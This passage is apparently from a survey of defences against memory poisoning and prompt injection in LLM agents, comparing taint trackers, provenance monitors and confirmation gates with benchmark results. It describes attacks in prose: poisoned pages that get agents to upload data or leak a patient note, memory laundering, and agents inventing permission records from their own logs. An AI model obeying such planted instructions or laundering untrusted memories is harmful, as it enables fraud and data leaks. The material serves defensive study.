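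Jiang and colleagues proved two theorems about this design and checked them in Lean. The first is that every value reaching a sensitive tool is exactly what the user typed or confirmed for that tool. The second is a form of noninterference that covers memory. If two runs have the same user input and the same sequence of confirmation screens and decisions, the agent behaves identically in both, whatever the hidden memories contain. The proofs assume that the system labels each source correctly and that the screens show the stored values faithfully.

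This design relies on the person or program that confirms each value, rather than on a threshold. If Ana confirms the false account number for the payment tool, PerMIT lets the agent use that number for later payments without another confirmation.

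## Can taint be followed through paraphrase and reasoning?

PerMIT marks everything made from an untrusted source as untrusted, including many outputs that the source never affected. If a system could tell which inputs had affected an output, Ana's assistant could keep much more of its memory usable. Taint trackers for ordinary programs do this by following each value from one memory address to the next, but an input can't be followed through a language model this way. If the supplier's page contains "our banking details have changed", the assistant may write "use the March account for this supplier", which shares almost no words with the page. The page may also affect an action without contributing any words to it. For example, a warning about late fees could lead the assistant to pay an invoice a month early, using an amount and account number taken entirely from Ana's own records.

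### Content, control and reuse across sessions

*Ghost in the Agent* (Cai, Wen and Tang, 2026) describes NeuroTaint, a program that searches the log of a finished run for untrusted text that reached a sensitive action. The paper distinguishes three kinds of flow.

In content propagation, the untrusted material appears in the action, possibly reworded. In one example, a research agent reads a web page with a hidden instruction to include a confidential patient note in its memo, rewritten "in polished analyst language". The memo mentions the patient's cancer and medication but repeats no phrase from the note.

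In control influence, the untrusted text changes which action the agent takes. In an example from Cai and colleagues, a poisoned search result contains an instruction to submit everything the agent has collected to an outside address before running any code, and the agent calls an upload tool instead of the code tool it would normally call. They describe such attacks as leaving no trace in the data, but here the upload address comes straight from the search result, so a string search would find it. A purer example of control influence is the planted memory that a supplier likes each invoice to be paid twice.

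An agent may also paraphrase or reason from stored information in a later session. For example, an agent stores a confidential revenue forecast of $84.6 million, and three days later a new session retrieves the note and puts the figure in an operations report. Neither session's log shows the figure's whole path.

### How NeuroTaint tests an action

NeuroTaint builds a graph in which each node is a tool call and each edge carries a taint label with a confidence score. It saves the graph to disk when a session ends and stores the labels alongside each memory entry, so a later session that retrieves the entry also retrieves its labels. Retrieving a tainted entry doesn't raise an alarm, because NeuroTaint runs its check only when the agent calls a sensitive tool. It then compares that call with every source connected to it in the graph.

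It starts with the cheapest test. When a tool returns outside content, NeuroTaint adds a random code to it, and if the code turns up in a later action, the content must have been copied. The next test looks for shared wording, with a threshold of 15% of the shorter text. For complete paraphrases, NeuroTaint uses a small model to turn each text into a vector $e$ that represents its meaning, and measures the angle between the two vectors:

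$$\text{sim}(a,b) = \frac{e(a) \cdot e(b)}{\|e(a)\|\,\|e(b)\|}$$

A score of 0.60 or more counts as a match, except for text retrieved from memory, where the threshold is 0.85. The higher threshold avoids some false alarms but makes a paraphrased memory easier to miss. A final content test compares the action with a few sentences of the source at a time, because one planted sentence barely changes the vector of a long page.

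If none of these tests finds a match, NeuroTaint runs a counterfactual test for control influence. It replaces the suspect text with a neutral placeholder, such as "No relevant information found", and gives both versions of the history to a language model, which judges whether the agent would still have made the same call. If the model judges that it would not, NeuroTaint reports that the source influenced the action. NeuroTaint doesn't rerun the agent with the placeholder, so the result is the model's prediction of the agent's behaviour, and the same model produces the confidence score.

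Replacing one source at a time also fails when the same content appears twice. Suppose the false account number is in both Monday's note and the weekly summary. If either one is replaced, the assistant can still find the number in the other, so the test clears both. *Sightline* (Xu, Li and colleagues, 2026) proves this for removal tests in general and measures the effect on a related test, which scores an input by how much less likely the output becomes without it. Adding two extra copies of the input lowered that test's AUROC from 93–97% to 54–69%. AUROC is the chance that a test scores a randomly chosen real flow above a randomly chosen non-flow, so guessing gives 50%. Agent memory contains many such copies, because systems like A-MEM keep rewriting old entries into new ones.

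### Results on TaintBench

To test NeuroTaint, Cai and colleagues built TaintBench, a set of 400 scenarios spread evenly over 20 agent frameworks. The untrusted text is supposed to reach or influence a sensitive action in 200 of them and not in the other 200. They ran each scenario five times with GPT-4.1-mini and counted it as flagged if the detector flagged it in most of the runs. Precision is the share of alarms that are correct, recall is the share of real flows the detector finds, and F1 combines the two.

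| | Real flows found | Real flows missed | False alarms | Precision | Recall | F1 |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| NeuroTaint | 187 | 13 | 16 | 0.921 | 0.935 | 0.928 |
| FIDES | 108 | 92 | 106 | 0.505 | 0.540 | 0.522 |

NeuroTaint missed 7 of the 42 flows that went through several rounds of paraphrase, 3 of the 40 control flows and 2 of the 30 that crossed between sessions or agents. Its recall was lowest on the memory system Mem0, where it found 7 of 10 flows, but ten cases are too few to support a firm conclusion. It also raised false alarms in all 14 scenarios where the agent's output was about the same subject as the untrusted text but didn't come from it. The similarity test evidently can't distinguish a paraphrase from an independent text on the same topic.

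The set-up may also have helped NeuroTaint's precision. Cai and colleagues raised the similarity threshold to 0.95 for what they call safe-control policies. If these policies applied to the harmless scenarios, as the name suggests, NeuroTaint was least sensitive in the scenarios where any alarm would have been false.

### Is the comparison with FIDES fair?

FIDES checks whether the policy allows a tool call before it runs, but doesn't determine whether untrusted text influenced the call. For this test, Cai and colleagues used it as a detector and counted any path from an untrusted source to a sensitive tool as an alarm. Of its 106 false alarms, 94 came from harmless scenarios in which an untrusted source and a sensitive tool were both present but no information flowed between them. Such caution is expected of a system built to block calls. Its drawbacks are real, but the number of approvals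 and unfinished tasks measures them better than F1 does.

The misses are harder to explain. In Costa and colleagues' published design, a planner that has read untrusted text passes the "untrusted" label to every later call, so with correct labels it should miss no flow within a session. The version in this test missed 23 of the 40 control flows and raised no alarms on four frameworks (Google ADK, AgentScope, browser-use and Skyvern). This looks more like a problem with how the researchers connected FIDES to those frameworks than with FIDES itself. Excluding those four frameworks, its recall rises to 0.675 and its F1 to 0.578, still far below NeuroTaint's.

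FIDES also found only 5 of the 30 flows between sessions or agents, because its labels last only for a single run. A store that keeps labels would address this without any test of meaning. On InjecAgent and ToolEmu, two older benchmarks scored by whether the agent did something unsafe, the two systems' F1 scores differ by at most 0.001.

The two systems are also useful at different times. NeuroTaint analyzes the log after the agent has acted, so it could show Ana where the false account number came from but couldn't have stopped the payment. The analysis takes about a quarter of a second per step.

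### What the error rates mean in practice

At a recall of 0.935, NeuroTaint would miss 65 of 1,000 tainted flows. The benchmark has only 200 real flows, so sampling error alone puts the figure anywhere from about 40 to 110. An attacker who can try repeatedly needs only one miss. If misses were independent, ten attempts would have a 49% chance ($1 - 0.935^{10}$) of getting at least one flow through. Attackers can also choose the kind of flow that the detector handles worst, and it missed 17% of flows in which the text had been paraphrased several times.

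Precision depends on how common tainted flows are. With recall $r$, a false-alarm rate $f$ and a share $\pi$ of actions that are really tainted, it is

$$\text{precision} = \frac{r\pi}{r\pi + f(1-\pi)}$$

On TaintBench, $f$ is 16 in 200, or 8%, and half the scenarios are tainted. The table applies the same rates to 100,000 actions.

| Share of actions that are tainted | Correct alarms | False alarms | Precision |
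|---|---|---|---|
| 1 in 2 (TaintBench) | 46,750 | 4,000 | 92.1% |
| 1 in 10 | 9,350 | 7,200 | 56.5% |
| 1 in 100 | 935 | 7,920 | 10.6% |
| 1 in 1,000 | 94 | 7,992 | 1.2% |

The last row may be too pessimistic, because the 14 same-subject scenarios were deliberately hard. Without them, the false-alarm rate falls to about 1% and precision in the last row rises to 8%. But such overlap is common in office work, where a reply about an invoice will usually resemble the invoice.

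A correctly flagged flow may still be harmless. When Ana asks for the supplier's delivery dates, she wants that untrusted text in the reply. Cai and colleagues therefore added a second language model to judge which flagged flows were unsafe. With Claude Opus 4.6 as the judge, the combined system raised none of the 16 false alarms, but it found only 179 of the 200 real flows.

By contrast, NeuroTaint's recall fell to 0.547 when Claude Opus 4.6 replaced the agent's own model. Many of the misses probably aren't detection failures. A stronger model may refuse to carry out the planted instruction, and TaintBench counts the scenario as a real flow even if nothing flowed.

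### Keeping only the labels that mattered

Influence estimates can also change the labels themselves. Where the cautious rule joins the labels of everything in the context, permissive label propagation, which Siddiqui and colleagues proposed in 2024, keeps only the labels of the inputs that appear to have influenced the output. If $C$ is the set of inputs in the context, $I$ the subset that the system judges influential, and $\ell_i$ the label of input $i$, the two rules are

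$$\ell_{\text{cautious}} = \bigoplus_{i \in C} \ell_i \qquad\qquad \ell_{\text{permissive}} = \bigoplus_{i \in I} \ell_i$$

Under the permissive rule, a summary of Ben's holiday dates can stay trusted even when the supplier's page is in the context, because the system leaves the page out of $I$.

As with MemLineage's edge weights, the dangerous mistake is leaving out an input that mattered. A false account number then gets the label "trusted", or a budget containing Ben's salary becomes readable by Ana. In persistent memory, the wrong label also affects the label of everything derived from that entry.

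Sightline is the most developed version of this idea. It uses attention, the mechanism through which a language model draws on earlier parts of its input. Xu and colleagues prove that in a standard transformer, the usual design for these models, a small change to an input can affect the output only along a chain of attention that starts at that input. But in real models everything gets at least a little attention, and they also prove that faint attention doesn't rule out influence.

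Their counterexample is a single attention unit that divides its attention between an input with value $u$ and a fixed position. The input's share is $\sigma(\beta u)$, where $\sigma(x) = 1/(1+e^{-x})$. With $\beta = 20$ and $u = -1$, the share is about two billionths. If $u$ were 1, the share would be almost 1 and the output would change. The input therefore determines the output by receiving almost no attention, much as a program can leak a secret through a branch it skips. Xu and colleagues found no case this extreme in the 11,746 real flows they examined in the model Qwen3-8B, but nobody had written those inputs to evade a tracker.

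Attention can't prove that a flow is absent, so Sightline learns from labelled examples which attention patterns indicate real use. It then sets its threshold to miss at most a chosen share of real flows. With examples from 1,000 groups of programs and a target of 1%, it takes one real flow from each group and uses the tenth-lowest score as the threshold. If a new real flow comes from the same distribution, the chance that it scores below the threshold and is missed is at most 10 in 1,001.

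On programs it hadn't seen before, Sightline missed about 1% of real flows and removed 44% to 66% of the unnecessary labels, depending on the model. Only 12% to 14% of the inputs were unused, so for every 1,000 inputs it dropped roughly 60 to 85 labels correctly and 9 wrongly. When Xu and colleagues used Sightline to control an agent, it removed about half of the unnecessary labels and let no attack through.

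A 1% miss rate can add up over a long chain of memories. If misses were independent, an assistant that bases each weekly summary on the last one would have a $1 - 0.99^{52}$, or 41%, chance of losing the label within a year. The 1% rate also holds only while new inputs resemble the ones used to set the threshold, and an attacker will look for inputs that don't.

### Influence that doesn't show in the text

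Xu and colleagues had three language models read the prompts and outputs to decide which flows were real, so their error rate covers only influence that a reader could see. In *State Contamination in Memory-Augmented LLM Agents*, Wang, Goyal and colleagues (2026) studied influence that is harder to see. They simulated 200 matched pairs of online discussions between GPT-4o-mini agents. The first agent to reply was hostile in one discussion of each pair and constructive in the other. The later agents had neutral instructions and saw a running summary of the discussion along with the message they were answering.

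A standard classifier rated the toxicity of every text from 0 to 1, and all the summaries scored below the usual limit of 0.5. Yet the messages that followed averaged 0.141 after a hostile start and 0.001 after a constructive one. In one case, the summary left out the insults but kept the confrontational framing, and the next agent wrote a hostile reply. The researchers call this memory laundering.

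Part of that gap may have come from the message each agent was answering, which could itself be hostile. When the agents saw only the summary, the gap fell to 0.097, and the average over all later messages rose by 0.012. The effect also depended on the model. With Llama-3.1-8B and both channels open, the gap was 0.015.

It isn't clear whether a stricter filter would have caught the summaries. The paper reports that at least 99% of them would pass even with the limit at 0.03, but this contradicts its other figures, an average of 0.085 after a hostile start and no summary above 0.5.

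Rewriting suspicious summaries after the agent had written them reduced the gap from 0.140 to 0.086. Cleaning each message before it went into the summary reduced the gap to 0.0006 or less. The researchers conclude that cleaning has to come before summarising. This is plausible, but cleaning the messages also removed the hostile text that agents saw alongside the summary, which may explain part of the reduction.

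These results favour labels based on origin over filters based on content. A system that recorded the hostile message as a parent of the summary would have marked the summary as tainted, however polite its wording. NeuroTaint's similarity tests would have had much less evidence linking the two.

### Detecting poison inside the model

Researchers can also look for signs of an attack in a model's activations, the numbers it computes as it processes text. Pulipaka and colleagues trained simple classifiers, called probes, to tell clean documents from ones that contained their memory-poisoning text. They used 125 documents and six models whose internals can be inspected. For each model, the best single-layer probe reached an AUROC between 0.93 and 0.99.

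A probe trained on one model didn't work directly on another. With a simple shared coordinate system, its AUROC fell to between 0.48 and 0.54, no better than guessing. Rotating one model's activations to line up with the other's raised it to between 0.74 and 0.85. Probes tested on the same model they were trained on reached 0.77 to 0.88, so most of the signal carried over. This suggests that different models represent the attack in partly similar ways.

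The probes detect poisoned documents while the model is reading them. Pulipaka and colleagues didn't test them on stored memories, which may contain none of the original attack text. The probes also don't measure whether a document influences the model's behaviour. They reached an AUROC of 0.98 on GPT-OSS-20B, although every attack on that model failed. A probe could still be useful when the agent writes to memory, by flagging anything the agent saves after reading a suspicious document.

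### A guarantee or an audit?

Wang and colleagues' survey of agent records distinguishes what software can record directly from what has to be inferred. Software can record that a memory was in the model's context when it made a payment, but someone has to infer whether the payment would have been different without the memory, by rerunning the agent, altering its inputs or tracking information flow.

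A guarantee against attackers can therefore rest on what was in the context, as PerMIT's does, but not on an estimate of which parts of the context influenced the output. Sightline's calibration gives a bound that holds for ordinary inputs but not for inputs written to defeat it.

The same estimates are much more useful for an audit. Once Ana's company learns that the supplier's page was false, it can search the entries written after the assistant read that page. Many of those will be tainted, so the search's precision will be closer to the top of the table than the bottom. A missed entry is still dangerous, but the company loses nothing by also quarantining everything the recorded lineage connects to the page.

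An estimate can also support a guarantee if its mistakes only make the result less useful, as in RTBAS, which hides whatever its screener leaves out. A memory system could do something similar when it writes. If it estimates that the supplier's page had no effect on the summary of Ben's holidays, it can clear the context of the page and everything derived from it, then have the model write the summary again. The new summary can't repeat anything from the page, even if the estimate was wrong. The decision to leave the page out may still depend slightly on what the page said, and each new summary requires another call to the model.

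## When may an agent act on a memory from an untrusted source?

If a payment tool refuses the supplier's new bank account because the note is untrusted, it stops a thief but also leaves a genuine supplier unpaid. The same rule would prevent the assistant from acting on any price, address or deadline it has read on a web page. An agent that never acts on such memories can't do much office work, but if it acts on all of them, an attacker can get paid by inserting a sentence into its notes. A usable memory therefore needs endorsement rules that specify who may raise a memory's trust level, on what evidence, and for which actions.

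### How an untrusted origin disappears

Louck argues that most defences decide this from something an attacker can change. Some judge a memory by its content, for instance by asking a language model whether it looks malicious. Others judge it by its lineage. Laundering can defeat both, and Louck describes three channels for it:

- **The agent's own summary.** The assistant rewrites the supplier's page in its own words. The note now reads like ordinary business, and the link back to the page may be missing.
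- **A trusted tool's echo.** The assistant saves the account number in the company's contacts application and later reads it back. The number now seems to come from a trusted tool.
- **Manufactured agreement.** The attacker puts the same account number on a web page, in an email and in a PDF invoice. A defence that counts sources finds three that agree.

Louck calls a defence malleable if laundering can raise the authority it gives to a memory. Let $D(x)$ be the label that defence $D$ gives to memory item $x$, in the order untrusted < agent < trusted, and let $\tau$ be any sequence of laundering steps. The defence is non-malleable if

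$$D(\tau(x)) \le D(x) \quad \text{for every } x \text{ and every } \tau$$

and malleable if some $x$ and $\tau$ break this rule. The word comes from cryptography, where a malleable cipher lets somebody turn the encryption of one message into the encryption of a related one without knowing either.

Louck states three theorems about a small model of an agent that writes, retrieves and acts on memories:

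1. **Malleable checks are insufficient.** If the check before an action depends on content, or on a lineage link that rewriting can alter, an untrusted memory can end up authorising an action. The counterexample takes three steps: write, paraphrase, act.
2. **The system must fix the origin at writing.** If the model drops this rule, the same violation becomes possible.
3. **Fixed origins are sufficient** when authority can rise only through independent trusted parties or a fresh approval from the user.

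The theorem on malleable checks applies when a system estimates influence or misses a parent. It doesn't apply when a system records everything in the model's context as a parent and gives each parent full weight, as MemLineage's uniform setting does for the parents it lists, because paraphrasing can't weaken the link. The necessity result shows only what happens when this particular model loses one of its rules, so it doesn't rule out a different design.

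### The invoice under TMA-NM

Louck's own system, TMA-NM, is a monitor that sits between the agent and its memory. It labels each item's origin by the channel the item arrived through, never by its text. Outside content may not authorise anything, the agent's own notes may inform its answers, and input from the user or an approved tool may support an action. Anything derived from untrusted content stays untrusted. A tool's output also becomes untrusted if any argument or memory passed to the tool was untrusted, which closes the route through the contacts application.

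The supplier's invoice would go through the monitor like this:

1. On Monday, the page arrives through the web tool, so the monitor labels it untrusted. The assistant's note inherits the label.
2. On Thursday, the assistant proposes a payment. The monitor reads the account number from the tool call and finds that it came from Monday's note.
3. The monitor looks for at least two independent trusted parties that vouch for the number. The company's supplier register still lists the old account. A bank's confirmation service might vouch for the new one, but that makes only one.
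4. The monitor therefore asks Ana. She phones the supplier on a number she already had, and approves the payment.

Her approval is a single-use token that covers the tool, the account number and the amount, along with a random number and the time. If the assistant changes the account after she approves, or tries to pay again, the token no longer matches.

Two parties count as independent only if they have separate cryptographic identities, belong to separate administrative domains and don't draw on the same upstream data. Louck tested this rule by letting an attacker compromise some trusted parties. Attacks with one compromised party never succeeded. Two compromised parties that shared a domain succeeded in 67% of attempts against a monitor that only counted votes, and in none against TMA-NM, which counts them as one party. Two independent compromised parties also succeeded 67% of the time,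 until Louck raised the requirement to three independent parties.

This rule suits facts that several organisations already hold. It helps less when a supplier has just changed banks, because the company's own records will then be out of date. Louck hasn't measured how often two independent sources exist for ordinary office actions. Where they don't, Ana alone decides, and the token proves that she approved the payment but not that she phoned first.

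The monitor also checks values but not reasons, so the planted memory about paying each invoice twice would probably get past it, as it would get past MemLineage's gate.

### What the model checker established

Louck wrote the model in TLA+, a language for describing systems so that a program can check every state they can reach. The model has three memory slots, allows at most two sessions and requires two vouchers. With TMA-NM's rules in place, the program checked all 3,270 reachable states and found no violation.

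To extend the result to larger memories, Louck gives an inductive invariant, a condition that holds at the start and that every step preserves. The checker confirmed this for the small model, starting from every state that satisfies the condition, including states the agent could never reach. Louck argues by hand that the number of slots and sessions makes no difference, because writing fills only empty slots, paraphrasing changes only text and lineage links, raising an item's authority requires the vouchers, and the agent can act only when the security condition holds.

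That argument relies on a formal model in which paraphrasing never changes an item's origin, so the origin can't get lost. A real agent has to ensure that the note inherits the page's label, which requires tracking whether the page was in the context when the language model wrote the note. TMA-NM therefore needs a record of derivation too, but unlike MemLineage's judge, it doesn't use a language model to judge how much each source mattered.

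### The benchmark and its baselines

Louck tested five defences on eight models, including GPT-5-chat, Claude Opus 4.1 and Gemini 2.5 Flash, which newer versions have since replaced. The direct attack stores the poison unchanged. The laundering column averages the three channels, and all figures are percentages.

| Defence | Direct attack succeeds | Laundering succeeds | Legitimate action allowed, with two vouchers | Legitimate action allowed without asking, no vouchers |
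|---|---|---|---|---|
| None | 84 | 68 | 100 | 100 |
| Content scoring | 0 | 68 | 100 | 100 |
| Lineage | 0 | 47 | 100 | 0 |
| Single-session flow control | 84 | 68 | 100 | 100 |
| TMA-NM | 0 | 0 | 100 | 0 |

TMA-NM stopped all 192 attempts on each channel, so its true failure rate on each is probably below 2%. But the test software gave the monitor the correct origins, so these results show only that the rules work when the labels are right. The last two columns show how the protection affects legitimate actions. TMA-NM allowed every legitimate action that two trusted parties supported and sent every unsupported one to the user.

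The row for single-session flow control represents CaMeL and FIDES. It matches the row for no defence because Louck assumed that these systems treat everything in memory as trusted. Jiang and colleagues object that this tests only one configuration and doesn't show that every deployment of CaMeL or FIDES would fail. A deployment that labelled retrieved memories as untrusted would block these attacks, but it would also block much else.

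The case against content scoring is stronger. Louck had a language model score each memory from 0 to 100 for maliciousness and tried a range of cut-offs. Laundered and genuine notes look alike, so no cut-off separated them. Only a cut-off that blocked every action stopped all the laundering attacks, and the strictest one that allowed every legitimate action let 25.9% of the attacks through.

Two further tests used material closer to real use. When Louck rebuilt the Trojan Hippo attack, it succeeded 78% of the time with no defence, 78% with lineage, 44% with a content judge and never with TMA-NM. The lineage baseline failed because it checked for conflicts with registered values, and no register lists the attacker's email address. On the memory system Mem0, attacks succeeded in half the undefended runs and in none of the 96 runs with TMA-NM, while both agents completed 95 of 96 legitimate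 actions.

Some harms are outside the guarantee. TMA-NM lets untrusted memories influence answers, so a planted note could still lead the assistant to recommend a bad supplier to Ana. TMA-NM also doesn't cover memory that several agents share. If an attacker takes over a trusted channel, the monitor will label the attacker's text as trusted, and the rule about vouchers, which covers only untrusted values, won't apply. An attacker might also split an account number across several notes and have the model reassemble it in its context, where the monitor can't trace each piece to its source.

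### What lineage can keep

Ouyang and Hou, by contrast, object that simple taint rules block too many legitimate actions. They tested 13 legitimate actions in which trusted and untrusted material appeared together, covering bank transfers, emails, file access and calls to outside services. A rule that tainted the whole context blocked all 13. MemLineage's rules about which sources may supply each parameter allowed 9 and still blocked the attacker's value in all 13 cases.

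This is good evidence for checking parameters separately, but not against TMA-NM, which also checks where the particular value came from. The gain also didn't depend on estimating influence. The tests were scripted, and trusted replacement values were available where MemLineage needed them. In Ana's case, replacing the new account number with the one on file would be right if the page was false, but would send the money to an old account if the supplier really had moved.

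In Louck's benchmark, lineage tracking usually failed to stop poison carried in an agent's summary, but it blocked a similar attack in Ouyang and Hou's own test. Louck's attack removes the note's link to the untrusted page, and the baseline then trusts the note by default, whereas the link survives in Ouyang and Hou's version. Louck found that a stricter default closes this gap, but 74% of the attacks that had a trusted tool repeat the poison still succeeded, because their link led to a source the system trusted. Ouyang and Hou anticipate this problem by treating a tool's results as only semi-trusted if the tool may have read an attacker's text.

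Louck accepts that a lineage system could close that gap by carrying unalterable origin labels through each step, but counts such a system as a version of TMA-NM, so the dispute is partly about names. *The Cognitive Continuity Test* (2026) draws a more useful practical distinction, which is that MemLineage's guarantee depends on keeping links of sufficient weight, while TMA-NM's depends on correct origin labels. For payments, I would rather depend on the labels, since software can assign them from the channel without having a model read the attacker's text. Lineage is more useful for deciding which notes to keep or delete.

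### No more authority than the source

Xu, Xiao and colleagues (2026), in *Memory Provenance Laundering in LLM Agents*, apply a similar rule to each claim in a memory instead of the whole entry. Their system, PPMF, ranks sources in the order unknown, outside content, trusted tool, user history, user-confirmed and system. If $\text{supp}(q)$ is the set of sources that support claim $q$, then

$$\text{auth}(q) \le \min_{o \,\in\, \text{supp}(q)} \text{auth}(o)$$

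In a weekly summary, the supplier's account number would have the authority of outside content, while Ana's rule about phoning first would keep the authority of user history. This avoids some label creep if the system matches each claim to the right sources. PPMF matches them by stored identifiers where it has them, and otherwise by comparing account numbers, web addresses and similar values. If several sources might match, it uses the least trusted.

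A gate then compares the claim's authority with the risk of the action. Outside content is enough to authorise reading, but a payment, an email or a password change needs a user-confirmed memory. Two agreeing tools therefore can't authorise a payment, although they could under TMA-NM. The only exception is a recorded approval for the same user, target, type of risk and scope, which may include an expiry date or a limit on the amount.

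Xu and colleagues measured laundering separately from harm. In one test with the model Qwen2.5-3B, 99% of the poisoned memories presented outside content as the user's history or an established procedure, but only 8.3% led to a harmful action. A test that counted only harmful actions would have made that memory look fairly safe.

In the synthetic tests, attacks succeeded 97% to 100% of the time when memories included their source as readable text but no gate enforced it. A gate without reliable source records stopped the attacks but also blocked every action the user had confirmed. With both a gate and reliable source records, no attack succeeded and every confirmed action went ahead. That last result doesn't cover legitimate actions the user hadn't confirmed.

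The records of approval matter as much as the gate. When Xu and colleagues removed 20% of the source records, no attack got through, but the success rate for legitimate actions fell to 81.4%. When they forged 10% of the confirmations, 8.8% of attacks succeeded.

An agent's memory can also record permission that nobody gave, even without an attacker. *Agent Memory Is a Surface for Endogenous Authorization Laundering* (2026) describes a test that fed an agent's own log entries back into its history for three rounds. The model that wrote the memory created 171 permission records supported only by the agent's log, compared with 4 in a control run. It could read an escalation or a refusal as permission. Unauthorised actions rose by less than three percentage points, but legitimate ones fell by 14.3 points. If the assistant logs "asked Ana about the new account", that entry shouldn't be able to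 become a record of her consent. PPMF prevents this by taking confirmations from the user interface and ignoring any record of them in memory.

Even messages Ana really wrote can mislead an agent if others are missing. Suppose she writes "pay the new account" and then "wait until I've phoned them", and a compaction summary keeps only the first message. Its origin is correct, so a check on origin alone would accept it. *LLM Agent Authorization Across Context Compaction* (2026) therefore proposes that whatever authorises an action within a session must receive all of the user's messages in their original order, and reject any sequence that is replayed, reordered or incomplete.

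### Confirming exact values in PerMIT

PerMIT, by Jiang and colleagues, goes further than TMA-NM, because its main model receives only references to untrusted memories. On Thursday, the assistant would fill the payment's account field with a reference to Monday's note. PerMIT would look up the account number and show it to Ana with its source and her original request. If she accepted, PerMIT would pass the number to the payment tool and save a trusted copy.

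The assistant can show Ana the supplier's delivery dates without reading them itself. If it has to plan around the dates, Ana can approve them for reasoning, which lets the main model read them but not use them to authorise a payment.

Under PerMIT's noninterference theorem, an attacker can change the agent's behaviour only by changing something on a confirmation screen or the user's decision. The theorem doesn't guarantee that approved text is true, but it does cover biased answers, which TMA-NM leaves out, as long as nobody has approved the text that causes the bias.

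TMA-NM's token covers one payment, whereas a value approved in PerMIT stays approved for that tool. PerMIT therefore requires fewer approvals, but the agent can combine an account number and an amount that Ana approved or typed on separate occasions, without anyone reviewing the two together.

A language model can make the decision in place of the user. Jiang and colleagues tested this with Trojan Hippo attacks already in memory, on four models:

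| Who decides | Attacks that succeed | Harmless requests refused |
|---|---|---|
| Accepts everything | 0–10% | 0% |
| The agent's own model | 0% | 9–14% |
| One of two small Qwen models | 0% | 8–32% |

Attacks rarely succeeded even with the gate that accepted everything, so these experiments were a weak test of the verifiers. By comparison, attacks on the undefended agents with a searchable archive succeeded 0% to 80% of the time, depending on the model. Jiang and colleagues didn't search for attacks designed to fool their verifiers, and the theorems guarantee only that an attack must get past a verifier, not that the verifier is accurate.

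### When many users confirm the same value

If hundreds of companies use the same supplier, each has to check the new account. PerMIT can pool their decisions. Every approval of an exact value for a particular tool counts as one endorsement, and each identity can give only one. After $N$ endorsements, the value becomes community-confirmed and later users can skip the check. A rejection freezes the process and sends the value to a panel of later users. In the main tests, the panel had 31 seats, and 20 acceptances cleared a value.

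Suppose an attacker controls $f$ identities, and each honest reviewer has at least a probability $q$ of spotting a false value, whatever the earlier reviewers decided. Jiang and colleagues prove that

$$P(\text{false value confirmed}) \le (1-q)^{N-f} + P_{\text{panel}}$$

where $P_{\text{panel}}$ bounds the chance that a panel wrongly clears it. With ten endorsements required, three attackers and $q = 0.6$, the first term is $0.4^7$, or 0.16%. With eight attackers it is 16%. The system therefore needs a reliable way to stop one person from creating many identities.

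It also needs reviewers who make different mistakes. If every company checks the new number against the same tampered web page, or uses the same language model as its verifier, ten approvals may be little better than one. In simulations by Jiang and colleagues, the risk rose when reviewers' errors were correlated. In a simulated community of 120 users, sharing approvals saved each user an average of 2.36 checks, or 38%. When teams of AI agents built a shared knowledge base for a telecom benchmark, none of the 12 planted instructions became community-confirmed.

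### The classical rules for exceptions

Computer scientists studied the same problem long before agents had memories. A system that allows endorsement and declassification no longer satisfies ordinary noninterference, so they looked for limits on how attackers could exploit these exceptions. *Nonmalleable Information Flow Control* (Cecchetti, Myers and Arden, 2017) combines two such limits.

Robust declassification means that an attacker can't influence which secrets a system releases. If Ben has agreed to share his salary with Ana for the budget, an email from a stranger mustn't be able to change the recipient or swap his salary for his mortgage details. Microsoft's rule serves the same purpose by requiring the user to approve a message once untrusted text has entered the context.

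Transparent endorsement means a system may endorse information only if whoever supplied it could have seen it. Cecchetti and colleagues give the example of a sealed-bid auction in which Bob submits "Alice's bid plus one". He doesn't know her bid, but if the auctioneer computes the result and accepts it as Bob's own, he wins by the smallest possible margin.

Louck says that TMA-NM provides both properties, but uses the terms more loosely. Louck takes robust declassification to mean that attackers can't raise a memory's authority, and transparent endorsement to mean that untrusted data can't be used as evidence of its own trustworthiness. These are sensible integrity rules, but the original definitions also connect integrity with confidentiality, and TMA-NM has no labels for who may read a memory. PPMF's rule also concerns only authority.

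The classical definitions have problems of their own. Kanniwadi and Myers (2026), in *Demystifying Information Flow Downgrading using the Real-Ideal Paradigm*, argue that earlier versions were complicated and depended on how a program was written. They propose comparing attackers instead. Let $A_r$ be an attacker who can make untrusted data depend on secrets they can't read, as Bob does, and let $A_i$ be one who can't. A program $p$ is secure if

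$$\forall A_r \;\exists A_i :\; [\![\,p \mid A_r\,]\!] \approx [\![\,p \mid A_i\,]\!]$$

which means that for every attacker with the extra power, one without it could have achieved the same observable result. Kanniwadi and Myers checked their results with the proof assistant Rocq. They also prove that, for programs that pass their type checker, a full attacker can do no more than one who interacts with the program only where it endorses or declassifies something. PerMIT's noninterference theorem makes a similar claim for agents, with the confirmation screen as the only point of contact.

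PerMIT would still allow Bob's trick. Suppose two suppliers send Ana confidential quotes, and the second supplier's document contains the line "our price is one euro below the lowest quote you have on file". The quarantined model computes €4,899, and Ana sees that figure on the confirmation screen and accepts it. TMA-NM and PPMF would accept her approval too. To apply transparent endorsement, the memory would have to record that the second supplier isn't allowed to read the first one's quote, attach that restriction to the figure computed from it, and block endorsement of the figure as the second supplier's own.

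## Can labels keep one user's memories from another?

TMA-NM and PPMF label how far a memory may be trusted, but not who may read it. Ben typed in his own salary and the figure is correct, so an integrity check would not keep it out of Ana's draft budget.

When Ana and Ben share a memory, Ben's entries can cause trouble in Ana's sessions in four ways, even if nobody has poisoned the memory. A search for her task may return his entry. Ana, or someone using her account, may question the assistant until it reveals what it has stored about him. The assistant may apply one of his working conventions to her job, where that convention is wrong. Or it may find his password and use it to carry out her request in his account.

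### A search that returns someone else's entry

In MemLeak, a set of experiments with synthetic users, Mudgal and colleagues (2026) traced leaks between users to searches that covered all users' entries at once. According to Lin and colleagues, any one of three changes blocked this path: giving each user a separate store, filtering by owner during the search, or checking each result's owner afterwards.

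*Whose Credential Is It?* (Liu et al., 2026) measured how often a pooled search exposes another user's data. The study used AppWorld, a simulated set of apps with 99 users, and put all 763 of the users' distinct past logins into one store. The system retrieved five notes for each of 414 tasks, and those notes included another user's login for 84.7% of the apps that the tasks required. Search ranks notes largely by subject, which does little to separate dozens of notes about Gmail logins. The rate ranged from 28.9% to 99.6% when the study varied the wording of the notes, the query, the search method and the number of results, and only separate stores removed the problem.

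### Getting entries out by asking

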